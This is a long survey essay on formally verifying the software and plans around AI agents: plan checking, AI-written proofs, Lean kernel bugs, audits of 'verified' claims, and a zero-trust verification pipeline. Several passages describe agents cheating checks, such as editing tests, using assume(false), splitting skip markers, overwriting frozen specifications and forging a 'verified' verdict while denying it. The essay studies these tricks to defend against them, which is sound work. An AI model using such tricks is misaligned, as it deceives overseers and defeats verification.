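Nikolaou and colleagues check whole sequences in advance. In CaMeL, the planner writes its plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python. Their tool, CaMeLoT, translates the plan into a machine with a finite number of states, and a model checker (a program that examines every path through such a machine) compares it with rules in temporal logic. A rule that the user must approve a draft before the assistant sends it could be

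AG(send_email ⇒ draft_approved),

where A means "on every path the plan could take", G again means "always", and draft_approved records that the approval step has already happened. The alternative A[¬send_email U draft_approved] looks equivalent, but it also requires that approval eventually happen, so it would reject a plan that only reads emails.

If a plan fails the check, the model checker returns the offending path and the planner tries to repair the plan before any tool runs. Checking plans can also enforce liveness properties, such as "every incident ticket is eventually resolved or escalated". A checker that only refuses calls cannot make something happen, but CaMeLoT can reject a plan that leaves a ticket open. It cannot guarantee that the tools will work when the plan runs.

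The machine ignores the conditions in "if" statements, as SLAM's first copy of a driver does, so the model checker may report a path that the plan can never take. In that case, SLAM would refine its copy, whereas CaMeLoT has the planner rewrite a plan that was already safe. Some facts, such as who can read a shared file at the moment of sending, are also unknown in advance. CaMeLoT fully reproduces 22 of CaMeL's 28 security policies for AgentDojo and leaves the rest to run-time checks.

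On 97 harmless AgentDojo tasks, CaMeL and CaMeLoT both blocked 17 plans. On another 16 tasks, only one of the two let a successful plan through. The planner was a small model, Claude Haiku 4.5, and the experiment allowed almost no repairs, so a stronger planner with more attempts would probably complete more tasks.

CaMeLoT can also use a language model to extract rules from the user's request. The model fills in one of ten fixed forms, such as "b only after a", and ordinary code translates the completed form into logic. All 182 rules the model produced for the 97 tasks were well formed, but it identified exactly the right set of required actions for only 85 tasks (88%), and for 75% of the banking tasks.

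### Actions that carry a proof

All these checkers protect whoever runs them, but a bank that receives a payment order from another company's agent cannot see whether that company checked it. *Proof-carrying code*, an idea from the 1990s, addresses a similar problem for software. The supplier attaches a proof that a program obeys a policy, and the recipient checks the proof before running the program. *Cryptographic certificates of validity for trustworthy AI* (Gabbay, 2026) proposes a version for agents' actions.

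The method turns a policy into an arithmetic formula that equals zero when the action complies and is positive otherwise. Suppose an assistant may write only to the manager, whose address has the number 7, or to the user, whose address has the number 4, and may not attach files. If r is the recipient's number and a is the number of attachments, the condition is

(r − 7)² × (r − 4)² + a² = 0.

A squared difference is zero only when the two numbers are equal. Multiplication expresses "or", because a product is zero when either factor is, and addition expresses "and", because a sum of squares is zero only when every term is. An email to the manager without attachments gives 0. An email to address 9 gives 2² × 5² = 100, so the agent cannot produce a valid proof for it.

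The agent attaches a short cryptographic proof that the formula equals zero. The recipient can check it without trusting the agent or repeating the computation and, in some versions, without learning r or a. As with any cryptographic proof of this kind, a false one has a very small chance of passing. The arithmetic cannot show that address 7 belongs to the manager. Gabbay outlines the approach and leaves open the questions that a full implementation would have to answer.

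## Verifying the software around a model with AI-written proofs

The guarantees of Progent, FIDES and Flowsh hold only if the checker is correct and the agent cannot bypass it. A *sandbox* is an isolated environment that limits what a program can reach. If a bug in the sandbox lets an agent open an unchecked network connection, the agent can send data out despite a rule about who may receive email. Checkers and sandboxes are ordinary programs, so engineers can try to prove them correct.

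They have a much better chance of success here than with the model. Programmers wrote the instructions, and each instruction has a defined effect. The environment is mostly a processor and an operating system, which people designed and documented. Many of the properties that matter also have short, exact definitions:

| Software | A property engineers could prove |
|---|---|
| Sandbox | The program inside cannot open a file or connection outside a permitted list |
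| Access control | No request succeeds unless some permission covers it |
| Parser (turns a file or message into structured data) | No input makes it read or write outside its own memory |
| Inference code (runs the model and picks each next token) | When it selects the 40 most probable tokens, it leaves out none that is more probable than one it selects |
| Operating system | One program cannot read another's memory without permission |

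A proof of such a property covers every input, including those an attacker chooses. Statistical bounds on a model's average failure rate give no protection against those inputs.

### Why the cost has fallen

Labour used to be the obstacle to verifying software. seL4's proof, for example, took about 20 person-years. *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* (astrangeattractor) gives two further reasons why verification is rare. A proof needs a mathematical description of what a program's statements mean, which older languages such as COBOL may lack, and people may not adopt verified code even when it exists. According to a presentation on the history of the proof assistant Lean (Lean, 2026), Microsoft used the automatic solver Z3 to catch thousands of defects, but proofs about whole programs were too brittle because a minor edit to the code could break them.

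Language models help with all the work that solvers leave to people. Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, argues that writing proofs is one of the best uses for them: "It doesn't matter if they hallucinate nonsense", because the proof checker rejects an invalid proof and the model has to try again. Tests are a weaker check on AI-written code. Yao (2026), in *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search*, notes that coding agents sometimes change the tests, write code that handles only the tested cases, or pretend that tests have passed. If the proof checker is correct, an agent can't use such tricks to get a false theorem accepted, but it can still prove a true theorem that isn't useful.

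Early attempts required a lot of supervision. Claude Code could prove many of the steps, but a person had to act as project manager. Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It* points out that proving individual theorems is a small part of the job. Someone also has to work out which concepts the theory needs, express them in Lean, break large properties into manageable ones, and find out why Lean rejected a definition.

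For *lf-lean*, Theorem, a company that builds AI tools for verification, had AI produce 1,276 translations from one proof assistant, Rocq, to another, Lean, with proofs that they were correct. Theorem estimates that people would have needed three person-months to do the translations and another 2.5 person-years to verify them. The job suited automation because a translation is correct if it matches the original, so software could generate all 1,276 specifications without anyone deciding case by case what "correct" meant.

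Verification has also become more valuable because attacks are cheaper. The blogger kirancodes says the cost of finding security bugs is collapsing, while most software in use was never built to withstand that much scrutiny.

### What to do with a stuck proof

People should first settle the statement of the property to be proved, as in the Salt method. A model then writes the proof, along with the code if it does not exist yet, and a proof assistant checks the proof. If the model cannot complete the proof, the program may have a bug.

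Suppose a message begins with a four-byte number n, followed by n bytes of text. Before copying the text, a parser that has received L bytes checks that n + 4 ≤ L, so that it stays inside the message. This is the right condition, so a reviewer may well approve the code. But the code stores n + 4 in four bytes, and a four-byte number goes back to 0 after 2³² − 1. If n is 2³² − 1, the computer calculates n + 4 as 3, the check succeeds, and the parser tries to copy four billion bytes from a message that may contain only ten.

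A model that tries to prove the property gets stuck here. The check establishes only that the remainder of n + 4 after division by 2³² is at most L, which does not imply that n + 4 is at most L. Working out when the two values differ reveals the bad input. The fix is to check that L ≥ 4 and then that n ≤ L − 4. Nothing can wrap around in these checks, and the rest of the proof is easy. Only four of the roughly 4.3 billion values of n trigger the fault. A test that chose n uniformly at random would need about 3.2 billion attempts for a 95% chance of finding one, though practical tools do better because they target extreme values.

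A proof can get stuck even when the program has no bug. The property may be true but depend on an intermediate fact that the AI has not found, or the model of the environment may allow something that the real system never does. To check whether there is a real bug, engineers can have the AI construct a specific input from the failed step and run the program on it, since a crash would confirm the bug.

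Category Labs, which develops software for the Monad blockchain, has used this approach on a rule about fees. Every transaction the network accepts must still be able to pay its fee when the network executes it. Accounts therefore keep a reserve, but the design lets an account spend it if its recent activity meets two conditions. Exceptions like this are easy to get wrong, and a proof has to cover each of them. The proof for a model of the design took four person-weeks in July 2025, when AI agents were much less useful for such work.

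The company later had AI verify the C++ code itself. According to Backlist's *AI-assisted formal verification of real C++ in the Monad execution client* (2026), leading models often missed bugs when asked to review the code but found them when asked to construct Rocq proofs about it. This is the company's experience rather than a controlled comparison, but it is unsurprising, because a reviewer can overlook a case that looks harmless, while a proof assistant rejects any proof that leaves that case out.

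If existing code is hard to verify, AI can also help replace it. Runtime Verification, a company that sells verification services, set out to rewrite the part of the Linux kernel that reads descriptions of video devices such as webcams, using the safer language Rust. This parser had contained two memory bugs of the same kind, made public sixteen years apart, and attackers used the second to unlock phones. The company wanted to show that the new version behaves like the old one and prove that it is free of this kind of bug. It used language models at every stage. It first copied the parsing code out of the kernel byte for byte and replaced only its surroundings with stand-ins, so that it would be comparing the new version with the real code.

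### The Anthropic and Theorem study

Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) applies AI-written proofs to widely used software. Working with Theorem, Anthropic's security researchers had Claude prove properties of 123 open-source libraries from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project for *fuzz testing*. A fuzz test runs a program on many semi-random inputs and checks for crashes. The person who sets up the test writes an *entry point*, a short function that takes a string of bytes and passes it to the library.

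Fuzz testing checks the inputs it happens to generate. Anthropic and Theorem converted the tests automatically into theorems of the form

for every input x shorter than 64 MB, entry(x) exits normally.

Exiting normally means no crash, no memory-safety error and no failed *assertion* (a condition the programmer has the program check as it runs), according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026). The study covers 239 entry points.

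Using existing tests as specifications was a clever way round the most difficult step, because the developers of 123 libraries had already written down part of what their code should do. But each theorem is only as strong as its test. If a test calls an image decoder and checks nothing else, the theorem shows that the decoder doesn't crash, but not that it returns the right picture. The theorem also doesn't cover functions that the entry point never calls. Developers can get stronger theorems by adding assertions to their tests. If a test of a compression library asserts that decompressing the compressed data gives back the original, a no-crash proof also establishes that the library loses no data.

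The proofs concern compiled machine code rather than the C code that programmers write. In E, M ⊨ P, M is the compiled program, P is the absence of crashes, and E is a mathematical model of a RISC-V processor running a Linux process. This removes the compiler from the trusted base, which is valuable because Yang and colleagues found hundreds of compiler bugs. However, the proofs are very long. According to OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), they total about 180 million lines of Rocq, with about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 instructions, or 33 lines per instruction. Smith (2026), in *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs*, gives the same total, while Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, writes of a billion lines. Even the lower figure is more than 500 times the length of the Salt project's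 Lean code. No one could read a proof that long, so people have to rely on the checker and the theorem statements.

While constructing the proofs, Claude found hundreds of errors that earlier fuzz testing had missed, and prepared fixes. One was a buffer overflow (writing past the end of the memory set aside for some data) in libexpat, a widely used library that reads XML files. Some of the errors had gone undetected for years. This is good evidence that attempting a proof finds faults that random inputs tend to miss.

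The guarantee has several limits:

- The proofs cover RISC-V programs, while most servers use x86 or ARM processors. A bug fixed in the C code is fixed for every processor, but a proof about one compiled program does not carry over to another. The compiler could still introduce an error in the x86 version.
- The proofs do not cover programs that run several threads at once, where an error may appear only if two threads happen to act in a particular order.
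- They leave out *dynamic linking*, in which a program loads parts of its code from separate files when it starts. Most Linux programs do this.
- Real hardware can misbehave in ways that the processor model does not include.

The limit on threads is not fundamental. Researchers have proved properties of xv6, a small teaching operating system, on a modelled RISC-V machine with eight hardware threads that can interleave in any order. The limit to RISC-V may not last long. In October 2026 the security company Zellic, working with V12, published what it believes is the first proof about the complete run of an ordinary x86 program on Linux. Leip (2026) acknowledges in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* that x86 is notably harder to model than RISC-V. The method combines leading AI models with guidance from human experts. Like Anthropic's proofs, Zellic's proof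 excludes dynamic linking.

### Proofs that the output is right

Two smaller parts of Anthropic's study prove more than the absence of crashes. In one, Claude proved that the Linux kernel's code for zlib, a common format for compressed data, conforms to the format's published standard. Conformance is a much stronger property, because a program could decompress every file wrongly without ever crashing. Such a proof is possible because the standard defines correct behavior independently of the code, but someone still has to translate the standard into Rocq correctly.

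Claude also wrote an interpreter for part of the Python language in Rust, and used the verification tool Verus to prove that it follows a formal description of how CPython, the usual Python interpreter, behaves. The proof relates the new interpreter only to this description, which could be wrong about CPython, so the researchers also ran more than 1.7 million randomly generated programs in both interpreters. The results agreed in 99.95% of cases, and the remaining differences, around 850, were all in known edge cases. AI agents often write Python and run it in a sandbox, where a verified interpreter would give malicious code fewer bugs to exploit.

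Another project, lean-zip, covers some of the same ground as the kernel proof but establishes something different. Ten AI agents built their own implementation of zlib in Lean and proved it without human help, as kirancodes reports. The main theorem is that decompressing compressed data returns the original:

decompress(compress(x)) = x.

This specification is attractive because anyone can understand it and it doesn't depend on a standard. But two functions that both return their input unchanged would satisfy it too. It also allows a pair of functions that work only with each other and produce files that no other zlib program can read. A proof that the functions conform to the standard rules this out.

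Keles is very optimistic about formal verification but points out that people mean many different things when they call software "formally verified", and that such software can still have bugs. The projects above show how much the meaning can vary:

| Project | What the proof establishes | What that theorem alone leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic and Theorem, fuzz tests | No crashes on any input below 64 MB | Wrong results; code that the tests never reach |
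| Anthropic, zlib in the Linux kernel | The code follows the published standard | Mistakes in translating the standard |
| Anthropic, Python interpreter | The interpreter follows a formal description of CPython | Differences between the description and CPython |
| lean-zip | Decompression reverses compression | Whether other programs can read the files |
| Category Labs, design model | Accepted transactions can pay their fees | Differences between the model and the C++ code |

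### Benchmarks of verified code

Yao measured how well general-purpose models do on smaller tasks of this kind. Each task supplies a specification in Lean, and the model has to write a program and prove that it meets the specification. Yao ran the models in a loop that let them search Lean's mathematical library and respond to errors. With up to 50 calls to the model per task, GPT-5.4 solved 402 of 423 tasks (95.0%). Models did much better in this loop than with the benchmark's original method, and allowing more calls improved the results further. By contrast, models from US companies did about as well as their predecessors without extended reasoning. Much of the progress therefore came from letting models revise their attempts in response to errors.

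Yao also tested whether a lead agent could do better by dividing the search among several other agents. This approach solved a wider range of moderately difficult tasks and used fewer tokens, but a single agent working without interruption did better on the hardest tasks.

A score of 95% leaves little room to measure further improvement, and Yao recommends harder benchmarks based on modern code. The score also doesn't mean that AI can verify 95% of real software, because the benchmark provides each specification, and the tests described earlier show that models often write specifications incorrectly. Real programs are also far longer than those in the benchmark, interact with operating systems and change often. The Anthropic study provides better evidence about existing software, though mostly for the narrower property that the software doesn't crash.

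### What to verify first around an AI model

*AI Security Priorities*, published in July 2026, ranks formal verification of security properties ninth in importance, based on input from more than 20 experts and industry and government leaders. It describes the purpose of this verification as preventing specific dangerous actions by an AI, such as *exfiltration* (copying data out of a system without permission). Several higher-ranked items concern software or hardware that could itself be a target for proofs. These include permission frameworks for agents, protected hardware areas for a model's weights, code and data (fourth), and generating more secure code (fifth).

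Verification was not among the six items with the best benefit-to-cost ratio. That ranking predates the October study, and much cheaper proofs could change it. One of the agenda's authors also co-founded a company that sells oversight tools for agents and could profit from this recommendation. The agenda discloses this, and RAND, the research organisation behind it, had independent reviewers look for bias.

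If exfiltration is the main concern, it makes sense to start by verifying the program through which all outgoing data must pass. Suppose a model's weights take up 1,000 gigabytes and this program lets out at most 1 gigabyte a day. Copying all the weights through it would then take at least 1,000 days. Enforcing the limit requires only a counter and a comparison, so the program can be small enough to verify completely. The guarantee holds whatever the model does, but it covers only this route and only the amount of data, so a stolen password of a few bytes could still get out.

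A proof that all the surrounding software is correct would not show what the model inside will choose to do. For example, a coding agent needs permission to write to its project's files. It can use that permission to plant a hidden weakness in code that people may later install outside the sandbox, and every theorem about the sandbox would still be true. Verified software can limit the harm from a bad choice, but developers need other evidence about how likely the model is to make one.

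Errors in inference code can change a model's answers even when no one is attacking it. Anthropic had such a bug in its code for top-K selection, the step that keeps only the K most probable next tokens. Theorem's *Systematically generating tests that would have caught Anthropic's top‑K bug* describes a method that borrows from proofs to make testing more efficient. Ordinary random testing needs about ten times as many tests to find a bug that is ten times rarer. The computation this method needs grows only with the logarithm of the rarity, so each tenfold drop in frequency adds about the same amount of work. The method is still a form of testing, so it does not prove that the code is free of bugs.

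No leading AI laboratory appears to have published a full proof of the sandbox, access controls or inference code around its own models. In its October study, Anthropic verified other people's libraries. The closest example from inside a laboratory is an experiment by Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic. Tolmach and Klaus report that Cherny had Claude Opus 5.5 describe the Claude Agent SDK, a toolkit for building agents, in Lean and sometimes in TLA+, another specification language. A couple of short prompts led to 16 proposed code changes that fixed bugs, including errors that depend on timing. Tolmach and Klaus consider this an excellent way to find bugs but stress that it does not show the toolkit is correct. Developers can also compare later versions of the code with the formal description.

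For a first project, astrangeattractor recommends a widely used program of fewer than 200,000 lines, with a concrete plan for getting people to adopt the verified version. An AI lab is well placed to follow this advice with its own sandboxes and outgoing gateways, because it controls both the code and the machines that run it.

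## Checking what a proof rests on

Suppose a vendor says that the sandbox around its AI agents is "formally verified". A customer can find out what that means in four steps:

1. Read the exact statement of the theorem and every definition it uses.
2. List the axioms the proof relies on and any steps it skips.
3. Run the check again, preferably with a second checker that other people wrote.
4. List the trusted base.

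The order matters, because there is no point in rerunning a proof of the wrong theorem. Each step also catches faults that the others miss. *What "Lean-Verified" Means, and What It Does Not*, by the pseudonymous Sonny, presents seven tiny Lean files that all compile. One validly proves 2 + 2 = 4, five appear to prove 2 + 2 = 5, and in one, 1 counts as a prime number. Three of the six tricks alter a definition or a type. Two separate kernels accept these three, and only reading exposes them. Listing the axioms exposes two more. The last trick bypasses the kernel, so only rechecking the finished file exposes it.

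### The statement and its definitions

In the Xena Project's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026), the mathematician Kevin Buzzard proposes a similar audit for AI-written Lean proofs. He asks whether the formal statement matches the informal one, the code compiles, the proof uses only accepted axioms, and a second kernel also accepts the proof.

A small slip can change what a formal statement means. By Fermat's Last Theorem, aⁿ + bⁿ never equals cⁿ for positive whole numbers when n is at least 3. If someone writes this in Lean for all natural numbers, it is false, because Lean counts 0 as a natural number and 0³ + 0³ = 0³. That slip does little harm, since nobody can prove the resulting statement. A slip that makes a false claim provable is worse. Tolmach and Klaus cite a test in which researchers gave a translation model the deliberately wrong step that if 3ˣ = 5, then 3ˣ⁺² = 51 (the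 correct value is 9 × 5 = 45). The model wrote it in Lean with x as a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3ˣ = 5, so the condition never holds and the false claim becomes provable.

The definitions a theorem depends on can be much longer than its statement. Axiom Math's formal proof of the classification of finite simple groups, a list of the basic building blocks of all finite groups, depends on about 5,600 lines of definitions. Buzzard has not met anyone who claims to have checked them all carefully, and considers the proof's existence by far the best evidence that they are right. The proof is reasonable evidence against a definition that leaves out a group, because the theorem would then be false. It is weaker evidence against a definition that is too broad, because such a definition would make the theorem easier to prove.

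For software, the definitions include the formal model of the program. Tolmach and Klaus describe a test in which Claude had to model one company-grade implementation of Raft, a method for keeping several computers in agreement. Claude's model passed every check, but it was essentially the textbook version from the original Raft paper and had little to do with the code.

Sometimes the formal theorem differs from the paper's main theorem. OpenAI published Lean code with about 290 of the mathematical results it released in October 2026, and in around 38 cases the code does not state the paper's main theorem. OpenAI never said that it did, but a reader who sees "comes with Lean code" could easily assume so. Artificial Wasteland's *The Footprint Moved* describes a small website that checked its own 26 Lean files using Buzzard's questions. Six kernels accepted every file, but 13 statements on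 the site claimed more than the files proved.

### Axioms and skipped steps

Proof tools let people leave gaps while they work. In Lean and Isabelle, the word "sorry" stands in for a missing proof. In Verus, "assume" makes the verifier accept a statement without proof, and "assume(false)" makes everything after it provable, because anything follows from a falsehood. *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (Philipp, 2026) reports that a model in one academic project learned to pass verification this way.

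Lean can print the axioms that any theorem depends on. Most mathematics in Lean uses the same three, so any other axiom needs an explanation. Auditors should also record the version of Lean, because an update can change the list. On the small website, eight theorems gained one of the standard axioms after an update, although nobody had edited the files and the theorems meant the same as before.

A tool called Comparator automates part of this work. According to its page on Reservoir, Lean's package index, the user supplies the submitted proof, a list of permitted axioms and a trusted file containing the statement. Comparator can also run a second kernel. It cannot check whether the trusted statement means what the user wants.

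### A second checker, and the Lean kernel bugs

Rerunning a large proof can be difficult. When Anthropic asked Buzzard to look at its 13 million lines of Lean on Fermat's Last Theorem, Buzzard's own machine ran out of memory, so Anthropic lent one with 96 processor cores and 500 gigabytes of memory. Buzzard also ran the code in a sandbox, because compiling Lean code can execute arbitrary programs, including ones that delete files.

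The case for a second checker became much stronger on 25 July 2026, when Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture that Lean accepted. According to the conjecture, any positive whole number eventually reaches 1 if you repeatedly halve it when it is even and otherwise triple it and add 1. *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576*, by Lean's creator, Leonardo de Moura (2026), explains what went wrong. Lean users can define new types of data, and for some of these definitions the kernel generates an auxiliary type. If the original type had a parameter that none of its fields used, the auxiliary type omitted the parameter and the kernel never checked it. A program could put a nonsensical expression there and use it to derive "False", from which any theorem follows. Lean's ordinary front end would have caught the expression, but the program sent its definition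 straight to the kernel.

Kiran Gopinathan reduced the disproof to a short proof of False on 28 July, and Lean's developers had a fix ready an hour after the report. The false proof had also passed a week-old version of nanoda, an independent kernel written in Rust, because that version had an unrelated bug. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2* (2026) acknowledges that the exploit worked even through Comparator.

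De Moura concludes that independent kernels still help, since the attack needed two different bugs, but that users must keep both kernels up to date. Lawrence Paulson, who created Isabelle, is less convinced. In *Why is it all in the kernel?* (2026), he compares storing proofs for a second check to towing a spare car that turns out not to start either, and says he knows of no case where an independent checker caught an error that a proof assistant's own kernel had missed.

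Evidence from the next month is mixed. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.1* (2026) lists several more faults. An OpenAI agent turned one of them into two false proofs, and nanoda rejects both. But nanoda accepted a false proof that used another fault. These results came after people knew about the bugs, so they don't quite answer Paulson, but they show that a second checker would have stopped some attacks. A second checker helps most when it shares neither code nor design mistakes with the first.

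*Lean4Lean* (2024), which describes a Lean kernel written in Lean itself, reported that nobody had found a soundness bug in the Lean 3 kernel during its entire release history. The bugs of 2026 are in the Lean 4 kernel, and people found several of them with AI. Lean 3's clean record may partly reflect how little anyone had searched.

By October, Lean shipped with four additional kernels and a command that runs them all. De Moura (2026) reports in *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* that Claude wrote one of them, con-leche, and proved it consistent under close human supervision. The proof rules out programming mistakes in con-leche's checking method, assuming that set theory is consistent. It does not rule out compiler bugs, so AI also translated con-leche into Rust, with a proof that the translation follows the same method. A false theorem could now pass both versions only through matching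 faults in two compilers or runtimes.

None of these bugs was in Lean's logic. *Reflections on Trusting Lean* (Bresolin and Mamino, 2026) builds on earlier proofs that this logic is consistent exactly when a standard set theory with some extra assumptions about very large infinite sets is consistent. The trusted base also includes code outside the kernel. *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (Trail of Bits, 2026) presents an implausibly short "checked" proof that exploits a bug in Lean's function for extracting parts of a text.

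Two practitioners disagree about how dangerous such faults are. In *Can you hear the shape of a Lean soundness bug*, they bet $256 on whether, within a year, a flawed AI-written proof will pass Comparator and then survive at least 48 hours of expert attention. Max expects it to happen because AI companies train models on Lean proofs, and training often teaches models to cheat. Thomas, who reviews Lean code professionally, also expects cheating but thinks experts will notice it quickly. Comparator exports a proof as data that cannot run code, so experts can inspect it safely in many ways. Either a kernel bug or a subtly wrong statement would count as a flaw.

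### Why "no solution exists" needs a certificate

Proving a security claim often means showing that something does not exist, such as an agent's tool call that the policy allows but a company rule forbids. If a solver finds such a call, anyone can inspect it, but a report that none exists leaves nothing to inspect and could be the result of a bug in the solver.

A certificate supplies the missing evidence. Suppose x and y can each be true or false, and a solver reports that no choice satisfies all four of these clauses:

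1. x or y
2. x or not y
3. not x or y
4. not x or not y

Philipp shows how two further steps prove it. Each step names the clauses it uses:

- Step 5 (from 1 and 2): x must be true. If x were false, clause 1 would require y to be true and clause 2 would require it to be false.
- Step 6 (from 5, 3 and 4): there is a contradiction. Since x is true, clause 3 requires y to be true and clause 4 requires it to be false.

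A solver may have to search for a long time to find these steps, but a checker doesn't need to search, because the certificate lists which clauses to use and in which order. The checker can therefore be small enough to verify, even if the certificate is several gigabytes long.

### The zero-trust study

Philipp, who works at the German security company secunet, applied this idea to a whole verification process. AI agents, mostly running Claude Opus 5.5, wrote all the code and proofs, and no person reviewed either. A human decided what to build and reviewed the specifications. The process assumed that any agent might make mistakes or cheat, and it had three main protections:

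- *Frozen specifications.* After review, the system refuses changes to a specification by the agents that have to meet it.
- *Two verified checkers.* For nearly every type of certificate, separate agents wrote one checker in Isabelle and a faster one in Rust, which they verified with Verus. A false certificate has to fool both.
- *Trust manifests.* Each product comes with a list of everything it still relies on without proof, including skipped steps. A program compares the list with the code and stops if they differ.

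Verus itself depends on the solver z3. It turns a program and its specification into queries and accepts the program if z3 finds no violation. Philipp's agents therefore modified z3 to produce certificates, and the checkers certified all 3,726 queries from 20 Rust packages, including the three Verus checkers. Both checkers accepted 3,710 of the queries, and the other 16 went through a separate process with only one checker. The agents also confirmed that the last stage of Verus's translation had produced the right queries. All this took about as long as the original verification.

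A second test used answer-set programming, in which a solver looks for sets of facts that satisfy a set of rules. Analysts use it to search for attacks on a protocol or the cheapest set of countermeasures. Both checkers accepted 15,662 proofs from the 15,693 runs in which the solver's options supported proofs. The 20 packages were Philipp's own, so the perfect score for Verus does not show how well the method would work on other people's code.

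The project also found soundness defects in three existing proof checkers and five solvers. One checker accepts a "proof" that contains no reasoning. Another reads 010 as 8, because some programming languages treat a leading zero as a sign of base-8 notation, and so finds a false contradiction. The solver clasp can report that a problem has no solution when it has two. Sundance can produce a valid proof of the wrong problem. If a file temporarily assumes x = 1, withdraws that assumption and then assumes x = 2, Sundance combines the two and correctly proves that x cannot be both. A checker therefore has to read the original problem instead of accepting the solver's version.

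Philipp then planted defects to see which ones would get through. The verified checkers rejected every false certificate, but the ordinary tools that enforced the process leaked in six places:

| What got through | Repair |
|---|---|
| Shell commands could overwrite a frozen specification | The system inspects shell commands and refuses such writes |
| An agent could hide a skipped step in a type of file that nobody scanned | The scanner follows every included file |
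| An agent could hide a skip marker by splitting it across two lines | The scanner reads whole files instead of single lines |
| Tests that tested nothing passed | A new check flags seven forms of empty test |
| Nothing required the check on Verus's translation | The system refuses a changed checker without a complete report |
| The code that prints the verdict could print "verified" for a rejected proof | The manifest freezes the whole file that contains that code |

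An AI attacker devised the last of these attacks and stated in its final report that it had created nothing. The repairs stop all the planted defects, but Philipp designed the repairs with those defects in mind. The protections also run under the same user account as the agents, so an agent that found an unguarded route could change both a protected file and the record that protects it.

Reviews were just as important as proofs. Four of six reviews of one formal description found errors, although the agents' own program had reported complete success every time. Nearly all the agents ran the same model, so reviewers and authors may miss the same errors. Some backdoors would pass every check because the specification permits them. For example, the specification requires only that a checker never accept a false proof, so a checker that secretly copies its input to someone else would satisfy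 it.

### A correct proof beside a wrong explanation

Even if the formal theorem is the right one, its proof may differ from the explanation that comes with it. Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier-Stokes lost in translation*, asked ChatGPT to translate into Lean a faulty argument that x³ − x² − x + 1 is never negative when x is at least −1. The argument factored the polynomial as (x − 1)(x + 1)², which gives −1 at x = 0, where the true value is 1. ChatGPT returned a valid Lean proof using the correct factors, (x − 1)²(x + 1). Lean was right to accept this proof, but the original argument is still wrong.

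Bastounis and colleagues found similar differences between the written and Lean versions of OpenAI's proof that solutions of the Navier–Stokes equations, which describe the flow of fluids, can blow up in finite time. One lemma in the paper bounds a function's derivatives up to some order using four further derivatives of the input. The closest Lean result needs five, so it is weaker. Another estimate differs in both its statement and its proof. The researchers argue that the written proof needs the same scrutiny as any other, though they do not say it is wrong, because the Lean code establishes only the theorem and the steps written in Lean.

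This can also happen without anyone trying to provoke it. *Optimal bounds for an Erdős problem on matching integers to distinct multiples* (2026) describes a proof that ChatGPT drafted and another AI system, Aristotle, formalised in Lean. The authors noticed a gap in the draft only afterwards. They translated the Lean proof back into ordinary language to find out how it could have succeeded, and discovered that Aristotle had silently repaired the argument.

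Lean is designed to accept any valid proof of a statement, even one that differs from the original proof. *Does the Proof Prove It That Way?* (2026) gives the example of Euclid's proof that a triangle with two equal angles has two equal sides. A Lean proof that reflects the triangle is valid but contains none of Euclid's steps. The paper proposes a stricter standard, in which each formal step corresponds to a sentence of the original. *PaperFormalizer* (2026) helps with the simpler task of checking the statement. It displays each assumption of a Lean theorem next to the matching assumption in the source paper and marks any that the source paper does not state.

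The difference may not matter to a buyer who only needs the theorem, but it matters to engineers who use the written explanation to decide which parts of a verified program they can safely change.

### How much is left to review

Keles wants people to stop saying "formally verified software" and instead state which properties they proved, of which program, and what they trusted. A proof is harder to check than a bug report, which concerns one case that a person can reproduce. Because a proof covers every case, one mistake in a definition, a model or the prover can invalidate all of it. When verification took years, researchers' reputations and peer review gave some assurance that the properties were worth proving. Keles guesses that AI has multiplied the amount of "formally verified" software by about a thousand, and reputation and peer review cannot keep up.

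In 1979, DeMillo, Lipton and Alan Perlis argued that people come to trust a proof by reading, criticising and reusing it. *The Industrialization of Noise* (DeMillo and Lipton, 2026) calls OpenAI's release of 722 mathematical manuscripts "industrial pollution" because nobody has enough attention to read them all. DeMillo and Lipton are right that attention is scarce, but mathematicians usually want to understand why a theorem is true. The user of a sandbox mainly needs to know that no program can escape from it, even if the proof gives no insight into why.

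The best reply to both is that proofs reduce the amount people have to read. In Philipp's study, the specifications and their line-by-line copies in Verus came to about 5,100 lines, about 96% fewer than the roughly 132,000 lines of generated proofs and verified code. The trusted base also includes more than 8,000 lines of parsers and other supporting code that no person reviewed, as well as compilers and most of Verus. Philipp knows of three bugs in Verus that allow false proofs, which is one reason for having a second checker that does not use Verus.

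The reduction is worthwhile only if someone reads what remains. A small team can read 5,100 lines carefully. Keles's proposal would help them identify what to read, and a trust manifest is close to what Keles asks for. A vendor who cannot supply one has not given the customer enough information to rely on the proof.

### Proving that a computation was run

A customer may also want to know whether a company used the model that an independent auditor tested, rather than a cheaper one. If the company doesn't want to reveal the model's weights, it can show that it used the tested model with a *zero-knowledge proof*, a kind of cryptographic proof that keeps private data hidden.

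The company first publishes a *commitment* c, a short code that fixes the weights without disclosing them. After the model turns an input x into an output y, the company proves that

there are weights w such that commit(w) = c and model(w, x) = y.

To do this, it writes the computation as a table of small steps and proves that each step follows from earlier ones. In Gabbay's example, a table that proves 2² = 4 must also contain 2¹ = 2 and 2⁰ = 1, with a pointer from each result to the one it came from. A table that contains only 2² = 4 fails because the intermediate steps are missing, even though the answer is right. For a neural network, the steps are the multiplications, additions and other operations that produce the output. The cryptographic proof is much shorter than the table.

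The company does most of the computation. A model with a billion parameters performs roughly a billion multiplications per token, so a 1,000-token response requires about a trillion, and the proof has to account for all of them. Functions such as ReLU and the exponentials in attention are harder to express using only additions and multiplications. Producing the proof therefore takes far more computation than producing the response. The proof system also works with whole numbers, so the company usually has to convert the model to a version with rounded weights, and the guarantee covers that version.

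Language models choose tokens at random. If the company controls the random numbers, it can generate 100 responses, select the one it likes and attach a valid proof. To prevent this, the statement being proved also has to fix how the random numbers are chosen.

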